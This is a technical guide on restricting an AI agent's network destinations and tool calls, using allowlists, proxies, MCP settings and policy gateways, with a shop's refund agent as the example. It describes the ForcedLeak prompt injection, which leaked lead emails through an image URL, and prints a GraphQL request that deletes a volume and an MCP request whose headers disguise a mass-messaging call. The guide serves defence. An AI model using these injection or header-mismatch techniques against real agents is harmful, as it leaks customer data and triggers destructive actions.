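The shop's narrow tools contact fixed addresses, but only as long as their code is correct. A tool might build an address incorrectly, a server might redirect a request, or a colleague might add another general tool. A *destination allowlist* limits the damage in these cases by listing the only network destinations that a tool or environment may contact. The software that enforces the list blocks requests to all others. The list matters even more for an agent that writes and runs its own programs, because no developer has reviewed the addresses those programs use.

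Written instructions can't replace the list of allowed destinations. They didn't prevent the PocketOS deletion, and Anthropic's *Cloud environment setup* warns that an agent may try another way after a website blocks its request.

### The check, step by step

A reliable check involves more than looking for an approved name in the address. In simplified form, the code is:

```python
ALLOWED = {
    ("https", "api.payments.example", 443),
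    ("https", "api.hosting.example", 443),
    ("https", "hooks.chat.example", 443),
}

def send(address, request, redirects=0):
    url = parse(address)                                      # 1
    if (url.scheme, url.host, url.port) not in ALLOWED:       # 2, 3
        raise Refused
    ips = resolve(url.host)                                   # 4
    if not all(is_public(ip) for ip in ips):                  # 5
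        raise Refused
    reply = connect(ips[0], url, request, key_for(url.host))  # 6
    if reply.is_redirect:                                     # 7
        if redirects == 3:
            raise Refused
        return send(reply.new_address, request, redirects + 1)
    return reply
```

1. Parse the address once, and use the result for both the check and the connection. If the checking code and the sending code each parse the text, they may disagree about which part is the host. The check could then approve one host while the request goes to another.
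2. Require an approved scheme, which is the part before the colon. With plain `http`, anyone on the route can read or change the request, including its key. Some schemes don't use the network at all, such as `file`, which reads from the machine's own disk.
3. Compare the whole host name and the port with the list. A check that the host only starts with `api.payments.example` would also accept a stranger's `api.payments.example.stranger.example`. Without a port check, the request could reach a different program on the approved machine, such as an administration page.
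4. Look up the host's numeric address in the domain name system (DNS). This step has to come after the comparison, because a lookup sends the host name to outside servers, and the name itself can contain a customer's data.
5. Refuse private addresses and the cloud metadata address. Whoever manages a host's DNS records chooses its numeric address, and could choose one inside the shop's own network.
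6. Connect to the address that passed the check. If the sending code looks up the name again, it may get a public address for the check and a private one for the connection. Security researchers call this *DNS rebinding*.
7. Repeat all the steps for every redirect, which is a reply that tells the client to try another address. Many HTTP libraries follow redirects automatically, so if the code checks only the first address, an approved server can send the client to an unapproved one.

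At each redirect, the code also chooses the key based on the host that will receive the request. For instance, if the staff chat redirected a request to the payment company, the code would add the payment key, but no other host could receive that key.

### How published tools carry out the check

Docker's *Fetch Tool* documents a tool that lets agents read web pages with GET requests. If the developer sets `allowed_domains`, the tool refuses any other host before it makes a network call. It also checks the IP address as it connects, and by default refuses private networks, the machine itself and the metadata address 169.254.169.254. This blocks public names that point to private addresses, as well as DNS rebinding. The tool checks redirects against the same list and removes the developer's headers, which may contain keys, when a redirect leads to a different host.

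If an agent needs an internal service, its developer can turn off the address check with `allow_private_ips`. Doing only this would expose every internal system again, so Docker strongly recommends also listing the internal hosts the agent needs.

The fetch tool's address check has a documented gap. When Docker Desktop is running, it can send the tool's requests for Docker's own domains through a proxy. The tool first looks up the domain name and normally requires a public address, but the proxy then chooses the connection, and the tool can't confirm which address it uses. Whenever a proxy makes the connection, the proxy has to check the address.

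Docker also offers a *blocklist*, which refuses the listed hosts and permits all others. The same numeric address can be written in several ways, and Docker's text comparison doesn't recognise all of them. A blocked address written in an unrecognised form therefore gets past this check, whereas an allowlist would refuse it. Docker suggests blocking a particular address at the network layer to deny it reliably.

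The agent program gloamy has an `http_request` tool much like the one the shop removed, in which the model chooses the method, headers and body. Its published code refuses every request until the developer sets up a list of allowed hosts. It also rejects addresses that contain spaces or a user name, which could confuse a parser. But it extracts the host with its own function, then passes the original address to an HTTP library that parses it again. The host check also ignores the port.

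A larger gap is that gloamy doesn't look up a host's address before approving it. The code rejects a private address written directly in the request, but a hostname on its list that points to one would pass. Gloamy handles redirects more simply than Docker's tool by not following them. To try the new address, the model has to make another call, which goes through the same checks. The similar tool in ESP-Claw's *cap_http_request* accepts redirects only to hosts on its list.

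Port checks seem uncommon. None of the entry formats Docker documents includes a port, and OpenAI's and Anthropic's sandbox lists don't accept one. A developer who wants to limit ports may have to do it in the tool's code or a firewall.

### What a wildcard adds

A wildcard entry such as `*.example.com` covers every subdomain, including any that the domain's owner creates later. That is convenient when one company runs them all. But hosting services often give each customer a subdomain, so a wildcard for such a service also covers strangers' sites.

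The same entry can mean different things in different products:

| Product | `example.com` | `*.example.com` |
|---|---|---|
| Docker's fetch tool | The host and all its subdomains | Subdomains only |
| gloamy's `http_request` | The host and all its subdomains | Matches nothing |
| OpenAI's hosted sandbox | That exact host | Not accepted |
| Anthropic's cloud sandbox | That exact host | Subdomains only |

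A list moved unchanged from Anthropic's sandbox to Docker's tool would therefore allow more hosts. In gloamy, a lone `*` permits every public host, while Docker's tool rejects it when the configuration loads. It is safest to list exact hosts where the product allows it, and to test one subdomain that the list should block.

Anthropic's `allow_package_managers` setting also lets a sandbox download software from 36 hosts beyond those the developer approved, including GitHub, GitLab and Bitbucket, where anyone can open an account. Anthropic maintains the list of added hosts and can change it.

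### Where to enforce the list

A check inside a tool runs before the request is encrypted, so it can read the address, headers and body. But it covers only that tool, so an agent that also has a command line can run programs that contact hosts the tool would refuse.

A proxy outside a sandbox can restrict network requests from every program inside it. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes this setup for the coding agent Claude Code. The operating system confines the agent's shell commands and any programs they start, and their network traffic has to pass through the proxy. The model therefore can't get around the list of allowed destinations by writing its own HTTP client. The proxy doesn't cover Claude Code's web-fetching tool or its MCP tools, which have separate permission rules.

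By default, if the sandbox can't start, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it, and if a command fails because of the sandbox, the model may retry it outside, subject to the usual permission rules. An organisation that relies on the list should set `failIfUnavailable` to true and `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false.

Encryption limits what this kind of proxy can check. Claude Code's built-in proxy relies on the host name that the program supplies and doesn't decrypt the traffic. Anthropic warns that a program may be able to supply an approved name and still reach another host, and Docker gives a similar warning about its own sandboxes. Anthropic's remedy is a proxy that decrypts and inspects each request. That proxy can read every key and customer detail in the traffic, so it needs as much protection as the machine that runs the agent.

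An organisation can also enforce a list at the edge of its network, usually with a firewall. This covers all its machines, including any that the developer forgot. But a firewall generally can't identify the tool or conversation a request came from, and a cloud service's IP address may change or serve several companies.

| Place | Traffic it covers | What it can read | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
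| Inside the tool | That tool's requests | The whole request | Other tools and programs |
| Proxy around a sandbox | All programs in the sandbox | The host name, or the whole request if it decrypts traffic | Tools that run outside the sandbox |
| Network edge | All machines on the network | The numeric address and often the host name | Requests from other companies' machines |

### MCP calls that bypass the agent's proxy

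When a model provider's service calls a remote MCP server, the customer's proxy and firewall never receive the request, however strict their lists are.

OpenAI's *MCP connections* gives developers a choice. A server reached over HTTP can have a `connection_origin` of `service`, which makes OpenAI connect to it, or `environment`, which makes the connection from the sandbox where the agent works. To connect the help desk from the sandbox, the shop would write:

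```json
{
  "type": "mcp",
  "server_label": "help_desk",
  "transport": {
    "type": "http",
    "server_url": "https://mcp.helpdesk.example/mcp"
  },
  "connection_origin": "environment"
}
```

If the developer leaves out the `connection_origin` line, OpenAI makes the connection. Even if the shop then blocks all network access from its sandbox, the agent could still send customer data to the help desk's server in a tool call.

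Running the sandbox on the shop's own machines wouldn't change this. OpenAI's *Self-hosted sandboxes* describes a setup in which OpenAI still runs the agent's loop, and a program in the customer's environment connects to two OpenAI hosts to receive commands and return results. A firewall that allowed only those two hosts still wouldn't block any MCP calls that OpenAI makes directly.

Connecting from the environment brings the call under the shop's network rules, but makes the credential harder to protect. OpenAI's credential vault works only for connections that its own service makes. For a connection from the environment, the developer has to either put the credential in the configuration or have a trusted proxy add it. OpenAI recommends the proxy to keep credentials away from code that the agent writes.

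OpenAI's hosted sandbox can block all outside traffic or limit it to a list of one to 100 exact hosts. However, OpenAI requires unrestricted network access if the sandbox starts its own local MCP server. Access is also unrestricted by default, unless the session inherits a stricter setting from a template.

Anthropic's cloud sandbox applies its list more broadly. In limited mode, an empty list allows no hosts. The list also governs the web search and web fetch tools, although these run on Anthropic's servers. A session won't start if the agent has an MCP server whose host isn't on the list, unless the developer has turned on a setting that permits all the agent's configured servers. Because the list is shared, adding a host so the agent can read its web pages also lets programs in the sandbox send data to it.

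### Approved hosts can pass data on

A list of approved destinations controls only which services the agent can contact directly. Those services can then contact any other system. For example, the help desk's server could pass tickets to a subcontractor, and automation services are designed to start actions in other systems. If an approved MCP server offers a tool that fetches any web address, the agent can effectively reach the whole web.

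Anthropic advises developers to ensure that an agent with broad credentials for an approved domain can't use that domain to trigger other requests or leak data. Before adding a host, the shop should check whether the service can forward messages, fetch files from a URL or start automations. The shop can remove any of these functions it doesn't need from the credential. If it can't remove them, it should avoid sending the service any data that would do harm if it ended up elsewhere.

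### One host can serve friends and strangers

Many services put all their customers on one host, so an entry for `github.com` covers both the shop's own code and an attacker's. Docker warns that agents could send data out through such broad domains, and Anthropic gives the same warning about GitHub. A host list that permitted GitHub for ordinary work would not have stopped the ContextCrush attack, which sent private files to a GitHub issue.

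The shop's staff chat has the same weakness, because a stranger's webhook could have the same host as the shop's and differ only in its path and secret. The model can't reach that webhook through `post_staff_note`, but it could through a general tool with the same host list.

A proxy that can interpret a service's requests can restrict them more precisely. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes such a proxy for Claude Code on the web. The sandboxed program has a limited credential that works only with the proxy. Before adding the real GitHub token, the proxy checks this credential and the contents of the Git operation, for example to confirm that it changes only the permitted branch.

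An approved host may also allow harmful operations on the shop's own account. The payment company's host accepts payouts as well as refunds, and only the restricted key prevents a payout. Checking the full address wouldn't always help, because a GraphQL service such as Railway's uses the same address for reading and deleting data.

### ForcedLeak and the expired domain

Domains can change hands while still on an allowlist. Noma Labs, a research group at Noma Security, showed the danger with ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce's Agentforce agents. It published its findings on 25 September 2025, and Nytro (2025) reposted the full text on a security forum in *ForcedLeak*.

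The attack began with Web-to-Lead, a Salesforce feature that lets website visitors submit their details through a form and saves them as *leads*, or records of possible customers, in the company's Salesforce account. The form's description field accepted 42,000 characters, enough room for planted instructions. When an employee later asked the agent to deal with the lead, the agent also followed those instructions. It collected the email addresses of the company's leads and put them in the web address of an image in its reply. Loading the image sent the email addresses to Noma's server.

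Salesforce's web page had a *content security policy*, which tells a browser where it may load content from, and it should have stopped this. The policy allowed images from 22 domains, 15 of them listed with wildcards. One wildcard entry covered `my-salesforce-cms.com`. That domain's registration had expired, so Noma bought it for $5 and received the data at an address the policy allowed.

The image request could have passed every step of the earlier check, because its address used `https`, its host matched the list, and it needed neither a private address nor a redirect. A check on the host name can't detect that the domain has a new owner. Whoever maintains an allowlist therefore has to record who owns each domain and why it is listed, renew any registrations the organisation controls, and remove unused entries.

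A proxy around the agent's tools would have missed this request, because it came from the page showing the agent's reply. The shop should check whether its help desk loads images or link previews in replies. If so, the shop should remove images and unapproved links from the agent's text before the help desk displays it.

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July, and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later. Salesforce made its list of trusted addresses mandatory for these agents from 8 September, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. The Hacker News (2025) reports that Salesforce also regained control of the expired domain. Noma described its own demonstration of the attack and gave no evidence that criminals had used it.

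Salesforce still uses this approach. *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* says the product removes web addresses by default, and administrators add the ones they trust. Its example entry is `https://docs.google.com`, which also hosts documents written by strangers. The restriction would have blocked an unlisted image server, but each new entry needs a review.

### When the developer can't list every site

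A research agent may need to read pages that nobody can list in advance. For such agents, OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) proposes checking the exact address instead of the site's reputation. OpenAI builds an index of public web addresses without access to users' conversations. The agent can open any address in the index automatically. For any other address, OpenAI either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user before opening the link.

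OpenAI reasons that an address already public before the conversation is much less likely to contain the user's private data. An attacker therefore can't easily put a customer's email address in a link and have the agent fetch it unnoticed. A list of trusted sites gives weaker protection because a trusted site may redirect the agent elsewhere. OpenAI also argues that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

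A public page can pass this check and still contain false information or planted instructions, and OpenAI treats the check as one of several layers of protection. The check would also be a poor fit for the shop's API calls, because their addresses may contain order numbers and so shouldn't appear in a public index. The shop knows which services it needs, so a short list of allowed services is the better choice.

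### The shop's list of three hosts

The developer runs the three tools that the shop wrote in a sandbox and blocks every route out except a proxy. The proxy accepts only encrypted connections on port 443 to these hosts:

- `api.payments.example`, for looking up payments and making refunds
- `api.hosting.example`, for restarting the web service
- `hooks.chat.example`, for posting staff notes

The proxy looks up each hostname and makes the connection itself, so it connects to the address it checked. If a server redirects a tool to another host, the tool has to request a new connection and the proxy repeats the check. The host program connects separately to the model provider and the help desk's MCP server, at addresses the model can't change.

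The developer then sends six test requests through the proxy, using a test account for the refunds. Some imitate a broken tool by making requests that the shop's tools shouldn't produce in normal use.

| Test request | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Refund $40 for the broken lamp in order 5127 through `api.payments.example` | Allowed | The host and port are on the list |
| Send a customer's email address to `stats.stranger.example` | Refused | The host isn't on the list |
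| Send a refund request to `api.payments.example.stranger.example` | Refused | The host only starts with an approved name |
| Restart the web service while a test DNS record points `api.hosting.example` to 10.0.0.8 | Refused | The numeric address is private |
| Post a staff note and follow a redirect to `files.stranger.example` | Refused | The redirect leads to an unlisted host |
| Refund $310 for the undamaged desk in order 5090 through `api.payments.example` | Allowed, but harmful | The host and port are on the list |

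The refund for the desk uses the same host, port and operation as the one for the lamp. Only the order number and amount differ, and the proxy doesn't check either.

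## Set rules for each tool and its arguments

The shop needs a *per-tool policy* to stop the refund for the undamaged desk and still allow the one for the broken lamp. This policy is a set of rules that allow, refuse or hold a call depending on its tool, arguments and circumstances. Software outside the model has to enforce the rules, because a model can read a rule and still break it, as PocketOS's agent did.

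The shop's developer puts the rules in a gateway that receives every tool call before the tool's code runs. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a policy system that developers can install either as a library inside the host or as a proxy in front of the MCP servers. The library can cover every tool, while the proxy requires no change to the agent's code but misses any tools built into the host.

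If a model provider's service calls the MCP server, the call bypasses the shop's gateway. By default, though, OpenAI's service sends an approval request before each MCP call, with the tool's name and arguments. The developer's program can respond to the request, so it could apply the rules at that point and pass only doubtful calls to a person.

### The order of the checks

When the model requests the $40 refund for the lamp, the gateway does the following:

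1. It identifies the server and the tool. Two servers can each offer a tool called `refund_order`, and Model Context Protocol warns that the names servers give themselves may not be unique either. The gateway therefore goes by the connection that the developer set up.
2. It looks for that server and tool on its list of approved tools, and refuses the call if they aren't there.
3. It compares the tool's current definition with the copy that the developer approved.
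4. It checks the arguments, first against the schema and then against the shop's records.
5. It checks the running totals and the history of the session.
6. It allows the call, refuses it, or holds it for a person.
7. It records the call, the decision and the rule that decided it.

The order keeps a call from having any outside effect until it has passed every check. If the gateway refuses a call, it returns an error that names the rule, so the agent can try something permitted instead. But an agent that learns of a $60 limit might refund $60 of a $75 claim and close the ticket, so the shop holds calls for refunds over the limit instead of refusing them.

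### Approve servers and tools by name

Leaving a tool out of the model's list makes the model less likely to call it but doesn't prevent the call. The model could learn the name `message_all_customers` from a planted sentence in a ticket, and the help desk's server would recognise the name because it still offers that tool. The gateway therefore has to refuse the call even if the host has hidden the tool. Refusing calls without hiding the tool is safe but wasteful, since the model may keep requesting a tool it can't use.

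*Attested Tool-Server Admission* (Metere, 2026) proposes a standard way to approve servers and tools. The May 2026 proposal began when the software company Enclawed wanted its agent to use Google's Gmail server without giving it access to every tool there. A server's operator publishes a small signed document that identifies the server and gives the level of sensitive data it may handle. Before the first call, the host checks that the signature is valid, that it trusts the signer to vouch for that level, and that the level is high enough for the task. A separate list limits which of the server's tools the agent may use. For Gmail, the list contains tools for reading mail and drafting messages, so the host refuses a request for `delete_everything` before anything reaches the network.

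Google doesn't publish such a document, so Enclawed relies on its own signed configuration for the Gmail server. Until operators adopt the format, the tool list is the more useful half of the proposal, and any gateway can have one. Metere says that approving a server doesn't stop it from misusing the tools it was approved for. The design also has no way to revoke a single signed document, and one edition of Enclawed's software only warns when a check fails. The system refused every forged document and disguised tool name in Metere's tests, but these were a vendor's tests of its own product.

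The proposal also includes a log in which each entry contains a fingerprint of the previous one. If somebody later edits an entry, the fingerprints no longer match, so people investigating an incident can tell that the log was changed.

### Pin the approved definition

An approval should apply to one version of a tool. To *pin* a tool's definition, the developer saves all of it, including the title, description, input and output schemas, and annotations. The gateway puts the definition into a standard form with its fields in a fixed order, then computes a *hash*, a short fingerprint that changes if any character does. The gateway recomputes the hash whenever the host fetches the tool list. If a tool's hash has changed, the gateway blocks calls to that tool until the developer has read the new version.

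The gateway should also give the model the approved copy, so that a changed description never enters its context. This also helps when tool lists are cached, because Körbächer warns that if a shared cache stores a tampered definition, every client may receive it until the cache entry expires.

OpenAI's service imports a server's tool list once and reuses it as long as it remains in the conversation's context. The service also returns the list to the developer, whose program can compare it with the pinned copies before approving the first call.

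If tool definitions are pinned, correcting a spelling mistake in a description can stop the shop's agent until somebody reviews the change. The hash also covers only the definition, so it can't detect changes to the code that the tool runs.

### Check arguments against the shop's records

A schema can require an order number and a positive amount, but it can't show whether the order belongs to the customer. Model Context Protocol requires servers to validate their inputs, but the payment company doesn't know the shop's refund policy. The shop's rule for refunds, in simplified form, is:

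```python
def refund_rule(args, session):
    order = shop.find_order(args.order)
    if order is None or order.customer != session.customer:
        return refuse("not this customer's order")
    if not 0 < args.amount_usd <= order.paid_usd:
        return refuse("amount outside the price paid")
    if args.amount_usd > 60:
        return hold("over $60")
    if not reserve(order.id, args.amount_usd):
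        return hold("order already refunded, or daily total reached")
    return allow()
```

The amount must be positive because a negative refund could lower the day's total and allow more refunds that day. `session.customer` comes from the help desk's record of who opened the ticket, and the price comes from the shop's order database, so the model supplies neither.

*NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) applies a similar principle in a gateway that checks calls against a company's written policy. The gateway takes facts only from tool results and the user's own messages, so if planted text leads the agent to claim that the user has approved a transfer, the claim has no effect. The shop has to be stricter still. It can't treat a customer's statement that the lamp cost $60 as evidence of the price, because the customer is also the person who would receive the money.

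#### What a rule for a generic tool has to parse

If the shop had kept `http_request`, the gateway would first have to work out whether a request was a refund at all. That means interpreting each part of the request exactly as the payment company's server does:

- The path may have several spellings. A server may treat `/v1/refunds` and `/v1/%72efunds` as the same address, because `%72` is an encoded "r".
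- Some servers let a header override the method, so a request that starts with POST may act as a DELETE.
- A JSON body may contain `amount_usd` twice, once as 40 and once as 310. If the gateway reads the first value and the server reads the last, the shop approves $40 and pays $310.
- Leaving a field out can change the request's meaning. Some payment APIs refund the whole payment if the amount is missing.

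A GraphQL request, such as one to a hosting company with an API like Railway's, needs a full GraphQL parser:

```graphql
mutation Tidy {
  first: renameService(id: "web", name: "shop") { id }
  second: volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...")
}
```

A rule that checked only the first operation would let this request delete a volume. The rule has to check every operation in the text and block the whole request if any of them isn't approved.

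Some generic tools, like Cloudflare's `execute`, accept a program. Nobody can reliably predict from the program's text which requests it will send, so the rules have to apply to each request as the program sends it. For all these tools, writing a safe rule soon takes more work than writing a narrow tool.

### Reserve the money before the call

A limit on each refund doesn't limit their total, so the shop also limits automatic refunds to $5,000 a day. If it checks that a refund fits within the day's limit, makes the refund, and only then adds it to the total, two calls that arrive together can both pass the check and together exceed the limit.

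Suppose the shop has refunded $4,970 today, and two copies of the agent working on different tickets request refunds of $25 and $30. Both requests are checked against the $4,970 total before either is paid, so both fit under the limit. The shop pays both, and the day's total reaches $5,025. With fifty copies, the excess could be almost fifty times the size of one refund.

The gateway has to reserve the amount before it allows the call, in a single step that no other call can interrupt. A database can do this:

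```sql
BEGIN;
INSERT INTO automatic_refunds (order_id, amount_usd)
  VALUES ('5127', 40);
UPDATE daily_total SET used_usd = used_usd + 40
  WHERE day = CURRENT_DATE AND used_usd + 40 <= 5000;
COMMIT;
```

The first statement fails if the order already has an automatic refund, provided the developer has set the database to accept each order number only once. The second statement changes nothing if the new total would exceed $5,000. If either doesn't succeed, the gateway cancels both and holds the call. The database updates the total for one call at a time, so in the example, the total checked for the second call includes the first call's reservation.

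If the payment company rejects the refund, the gateway releases the reservation, but if the reply is lost, the gateway keeps the reservation because the customer may have received the money. The gateway's total may then be too high for a while, and some legitimate refunds may have to wait, but the shop can't exceed its limit.

Counters need similar care because the client repeats a call when an MCP server asks for more input, and a gateway that counts requests would count that call twice.

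### Let earlier calls limit later ones

Some calls are dangerous only because of what came before them. The shop's agent normally sends replies, but if it has found another customer's address, its next reply could expose it. Once the agent has read private data, a session rule can block or hold calls that send information out.

The developer gives each ticket its own session. If `search_tickets` returns a ticket that belongs to another customer, the gateway marks the session and holds every later reply for a person to review. The mark stays until the session ends, so planted text can't remove it. MCP no longer has sessions, so the gateway must store the session's history under an identifier that the host supplies and the model can't choose.

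This rule stops the agent from automatically sending one customer's address to another, but it also delays harmless replies, such as those the agent writes after searching for how staff fixed the same fault before. The gateway could remove other customers' tickets from the search results, which would reduce delays but make the agent less helpful.

When the steps of a task are known in advance, separating the tools is simpler than tracking what the agent has read. OpenAI gives the example of comparing a company's public announcement with private customer records. If one request has access to both web search and the records, planted text on a web page could make the model look up a customer and leak their email address in a link it opens. OpenAI recommends splitting the task into two requests. The first has only web search and collects the public facts. The second receives those facts and can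 access only the records.

Planted text could still enter the second request along with the facts and make the comparison wrong. But that request has no web tool, so it can't send a customer's details to the page's author. The order matters because a web search made second could include private details in its search terms.

### Rules that read only the headers

A gateway that handles traffic for many teams may not be able to read every request in full. Under the July 2026 specification, it can apply rules to the `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name` headers instead. InfoQ's *MCP Goes Stateless* reports that ordinary rate limiters and firewalls can also use these headers. The gateway still has to decrypt the connection, because HTTPS encrypts headers as well as request bodies.

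A server can also have the client copy chosen arguments into headers. It marks each argument with `x-mcp-header` in the tool's schema, and the client sends the value in a header that starts with `Mcp-Param-`. If the payment company did this for the refund amount, the request to refund the lamp might include `Mcp-Param-Amount: 40`. Körbächer gives the example of a rule that allows each customer account ten database queries a minute and stops test machines from querying one region. Such a rule used to be too costly for many organisations, but now it needs only a few headers.

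Published arguments have some awkward limits:

- The server chooses which arguments to publish. It can stop publishing one, or publish a different one under the same name, so the developer should pin these markings with the rest of the definition.
- Only text, whole numbers and yes-or-no values qualify. A refund of $39.99 would have to travel as text or as 3,999 cents.
- The client leaves the header out if the argument is missing. A rule that depends on the value should refuse a call without it.
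- The client encodes values that contain characters such as "ã". Körbächer warns that a rule for "São Paulo" will silently miss its target unless the gateway decodes the header first.
- Anything in a header is visible to every gateway on the route, so servers shouldn't publish passwords or personal details.

All these rules depend on the headers matching the body. Under the July version, a server that reads the body must reject a mismatch with HTTP status 400 and the error code -32020. Older versions don't require this comparison, so the following request could get past a gateway that checks only the tool's name in the header:

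```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Host: mcp.helpdesk.example
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2025-11-25
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: get_ticket

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 7, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "message_all_customers",
            "arguments": {"text": "We are closing down."}}}
```

The gateway would see a harmless ticket lookup, while an older server would act on the body and write to every customer. Model Context Protocol therefore recommends that gateways reject requests that use an older version or don't name one. As an alternative, Körbächer suggests sending older traffic to a gateway that reads the whole body. Even with the new version, the server is responsible for the comparison, so a shop that doesn't trust a server should read the body itself.

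### Three systems and their test results

Researchers have tested several systems that enforce rules on tool calls, mostly on *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark with 97 tasks and 629 security tests. In each security test, an attacker plants text in material that the agent reads, such as an email or a bill.

#### Progent

In Progent, a language model reads the user's task and writes a list of permitted calls, with conditions on their arguments. Software then blocks every call the list doesn't permit. As the agent learns more, the model proposes changes to the list. For example, if the agent finds out that the user's name on Slack is `alice`, the model might propose permitting only messages for `alice`. An *SMT solver*, a program that settles certain logical questions exactly, checks whether a change would permit anything new. Changes that only remove permissions take effect at once, and the rest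 need approval.

Shi and colleagues report that Progent cut the success rate of attacks on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% when it approved every change automatically to imitate a careless user. The rate fell to zero when a person reviewed the initial list and the changes that added permissions. Only 6% of changes needed that review.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent still depends on a model to recognise malicious instructions in tool results. This criticism is fair when new permissions are approved automatically. If a person reviews each one, a deceived model can't add permissions on its own, although the person can also be deceived.

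#### CaMeL

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes CaMeL, in which one model writes a plan from the user's request alone and a second model, which has no tools, processes the untrusted material. A program carries out the plan, tracks where each piece of data came from, and checks each tool call against its rules before making it. Text planted in the untrusted material can change a value in the plan but can't add a step.

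According to that paper, CaMeL stops nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo, but agents complete fewer tasks with it. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls this loss comparatively modest, while Yu and colleagues put it at 3 to 32 percentage points, depending on the model. Developers must also rebuild the agent around CaMeL. In the shop, CaMeL would keep a ticket from starting a payout, but the order number would still have to come from the ticket, so the shop would still need its refund rule.

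#### NOMOS

NOMOS (October 2026) derives its rules from a company's written policy instead of the user's task. A model turns each sentence of the policy into candidate rules, and ordinary software repairs or rejects the ones that can't work. The gateway then makes each decision without a model, in a few millionths of a second.

Yu and colleagues compared NOMOS with Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks, using the same open model for the agent in every case:

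| Defence | Attack succeeded | Task completed, no attack | Task completed under attack | Model calls for the defence while the agent works |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.5% | 79.2% | 64.9% | None |
| Progent, with automatic rules | 5.6% | 62.5% | 52.1% | To write and update each task's rules |
| NOMOS | 0.0% | 70.8% | 67.4% | None |

Most of Progent's failures came from requests such as "pay the bill, like last month", which don't name the recipient. A list written from such a request can't identify the right account. NOMOS had a standing rule that money could go only to recipients the user had named or paid before.

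The comparison favours NOMOS in some ways, because the system's developers ran the tests, wrote the banking policy, and revised it after seeing how it affected ordinary tasks. The 16 banking tasks are also too few to show a reliable difference in how many tasks the two systems complete without an attack. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) identifies a flaw in AgentDojo that affects the scores under attack. In some tests, the planted text replaces information the agent needs, such as the contents of a bill, so the agent can't complete the task under any defence.

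A second benchmark, τ²-bench, is closer to the shop's work because its agents serve simulated customers under a written company policy. In the retail tasks, NOMOS reduced the share of changes that broke the policy from 30.8% to 6.9%, without significantly affecting how many tasks the agent completed. In the airline tasks, it reduced the share from 66.3% to 2.6%, and the agent completed more tasks, because breaking the policy often meant failing the task. These figures cover only the parts of each policy that the researchers had turned into checks.

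Yu and colleagues also tried having a model judge each call during the airline tasks. Agents completed about as many tasks as with fixed rules, but each simulation took 74% longer on average. For a shop with clear limits on money, fixed rules are the better choice.

### Who writes the rules, and what goes wrong

The people who know the refund policy usually don't write software. At the shop, the head of customer service decides the limits, the developer turns them into code, and each checks the other's work. Neither should let the agent edit the rules.

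The developer can write the rules in ordinary code or in a *policy language* such as Cedar, which is designed for access rules. Because a policy language limits what the rules can express, other software can check them for problems such as conflicts. The developer still needs other code to look up orders and reserve money. Ordinary code is enough for the shop's six tools, but a company with hundreds would gain more from a policy language.

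Having a model write the rules saves work but introduces errors. In one of Yu and colleagues' tests, the model turned the sentence "authenticate the user before any action" into a rule that blocked every tool, including the login tools, until the user had logged in. Without automatic checks, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could never have worked. A larger commercial model made some of the same kinds of mistakes.

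#### Wrong refusals

A rule can also work as written but refuse calls it should allow. A telecoms policy required staff to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment. The model turned this into a ban on requesting payment while a bill was overdue, which is when a company should request it. Yu and colleagues found the error by running the rule on recorded calls from an agent without rules. The rule would have refused 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs. The shop can test its own rules on last month's refunds before switching them on.

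Stricter rules can also stop an agent from doing ordinary work. In AgentDojo's Slack tasks, attacks still succeeded in 15 of 105 tests under the NOMOS rules. One fix to the rules stopped all of these attacks but cut the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 57.1% to 14.3%. Many of those tasks require the agent to act on names and addresses it finds while reading, and the attacks rely on the same behavior.

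#### Harmful calls that pass every rule

The 0.0% in the table counts only attacks that reached the attacker's goal. In 8 of the 288 tests, planted text still caused a payment that the user hadn't asked for. The rules allowed it because the user had paid the recipient before, which is weak evidence that the user wanted this payment. With a different model, one agent made four such payments of $10,000 each during a task in which the user had only asked a question.

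Rules also can't enforce parts of a policy that nobody turned into rules. In the retail tasks, 21 of the 40 remaining violations involved two parts of the policy that NOMOS had missed. One of them concerned where a refund may go. The shop's `refund_order` tool has no argument for the destination, so an agent using it can't choose where the refund goes.

### The shop's policy

The head of customer service allows automatic refunds of up to $60 each, with at most one per order and a total of $5,000 a day. On a normal day, 130 of the shop's 150 refunds are for $60 or less. They average $30 and total $3,900, which leaves $1,100 of the daily limit for busy days. The other 20 refunds average $105 and need a person's approval.

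| Tool | The gateway allows | The gateway holds | The gateway refuses |
|---|---|---|---|
| `refund_order` | Up to $60, for an order without an earlier automatic refund, within the $5,000 total | Larger refunds, a second refund for an order, and any refund that would exceed the total | Another customer's order, or more than the customer paid |
| `restart_web_service` | One restart an hour | Further restarts | Any argument |
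| `post_staff_note` | Up to 20 notes an hour | Further notes | Notes that contain links |
| `get_ticket` | The ticket that the session is about | Nothing | Other tickets |
| `search_tickets` | All searches, with a mark on the session if another customer's ticket appears | Nothing | Nothing |
| `reply_to_ticket` | Replies to the session's ticket | Replies in a marked session | Replies to other tickets |
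| Any other tool | Nothing | Nothing | Every call |

The $40 refund for the lamp goes through, and the $310 refund for the desk now waits for a person to review it. The agent can't avoid review by splitting the desk's price into smaller refunds, because the second refund for the same order would also be held.

Before these rules, an agent that got stuck in a loop or followed planted text could have refunded recent orders until the $80,000 balance was gone. Now automatic refunds stop at $5,000 a day, regardless of how many copies of the agent are running or what the tickets contain. At $60 each, the agent would have to refund 84 different orders to reach that limit, with a smaller refund for the last one. The limit doesn't cover refunds that a person approves.

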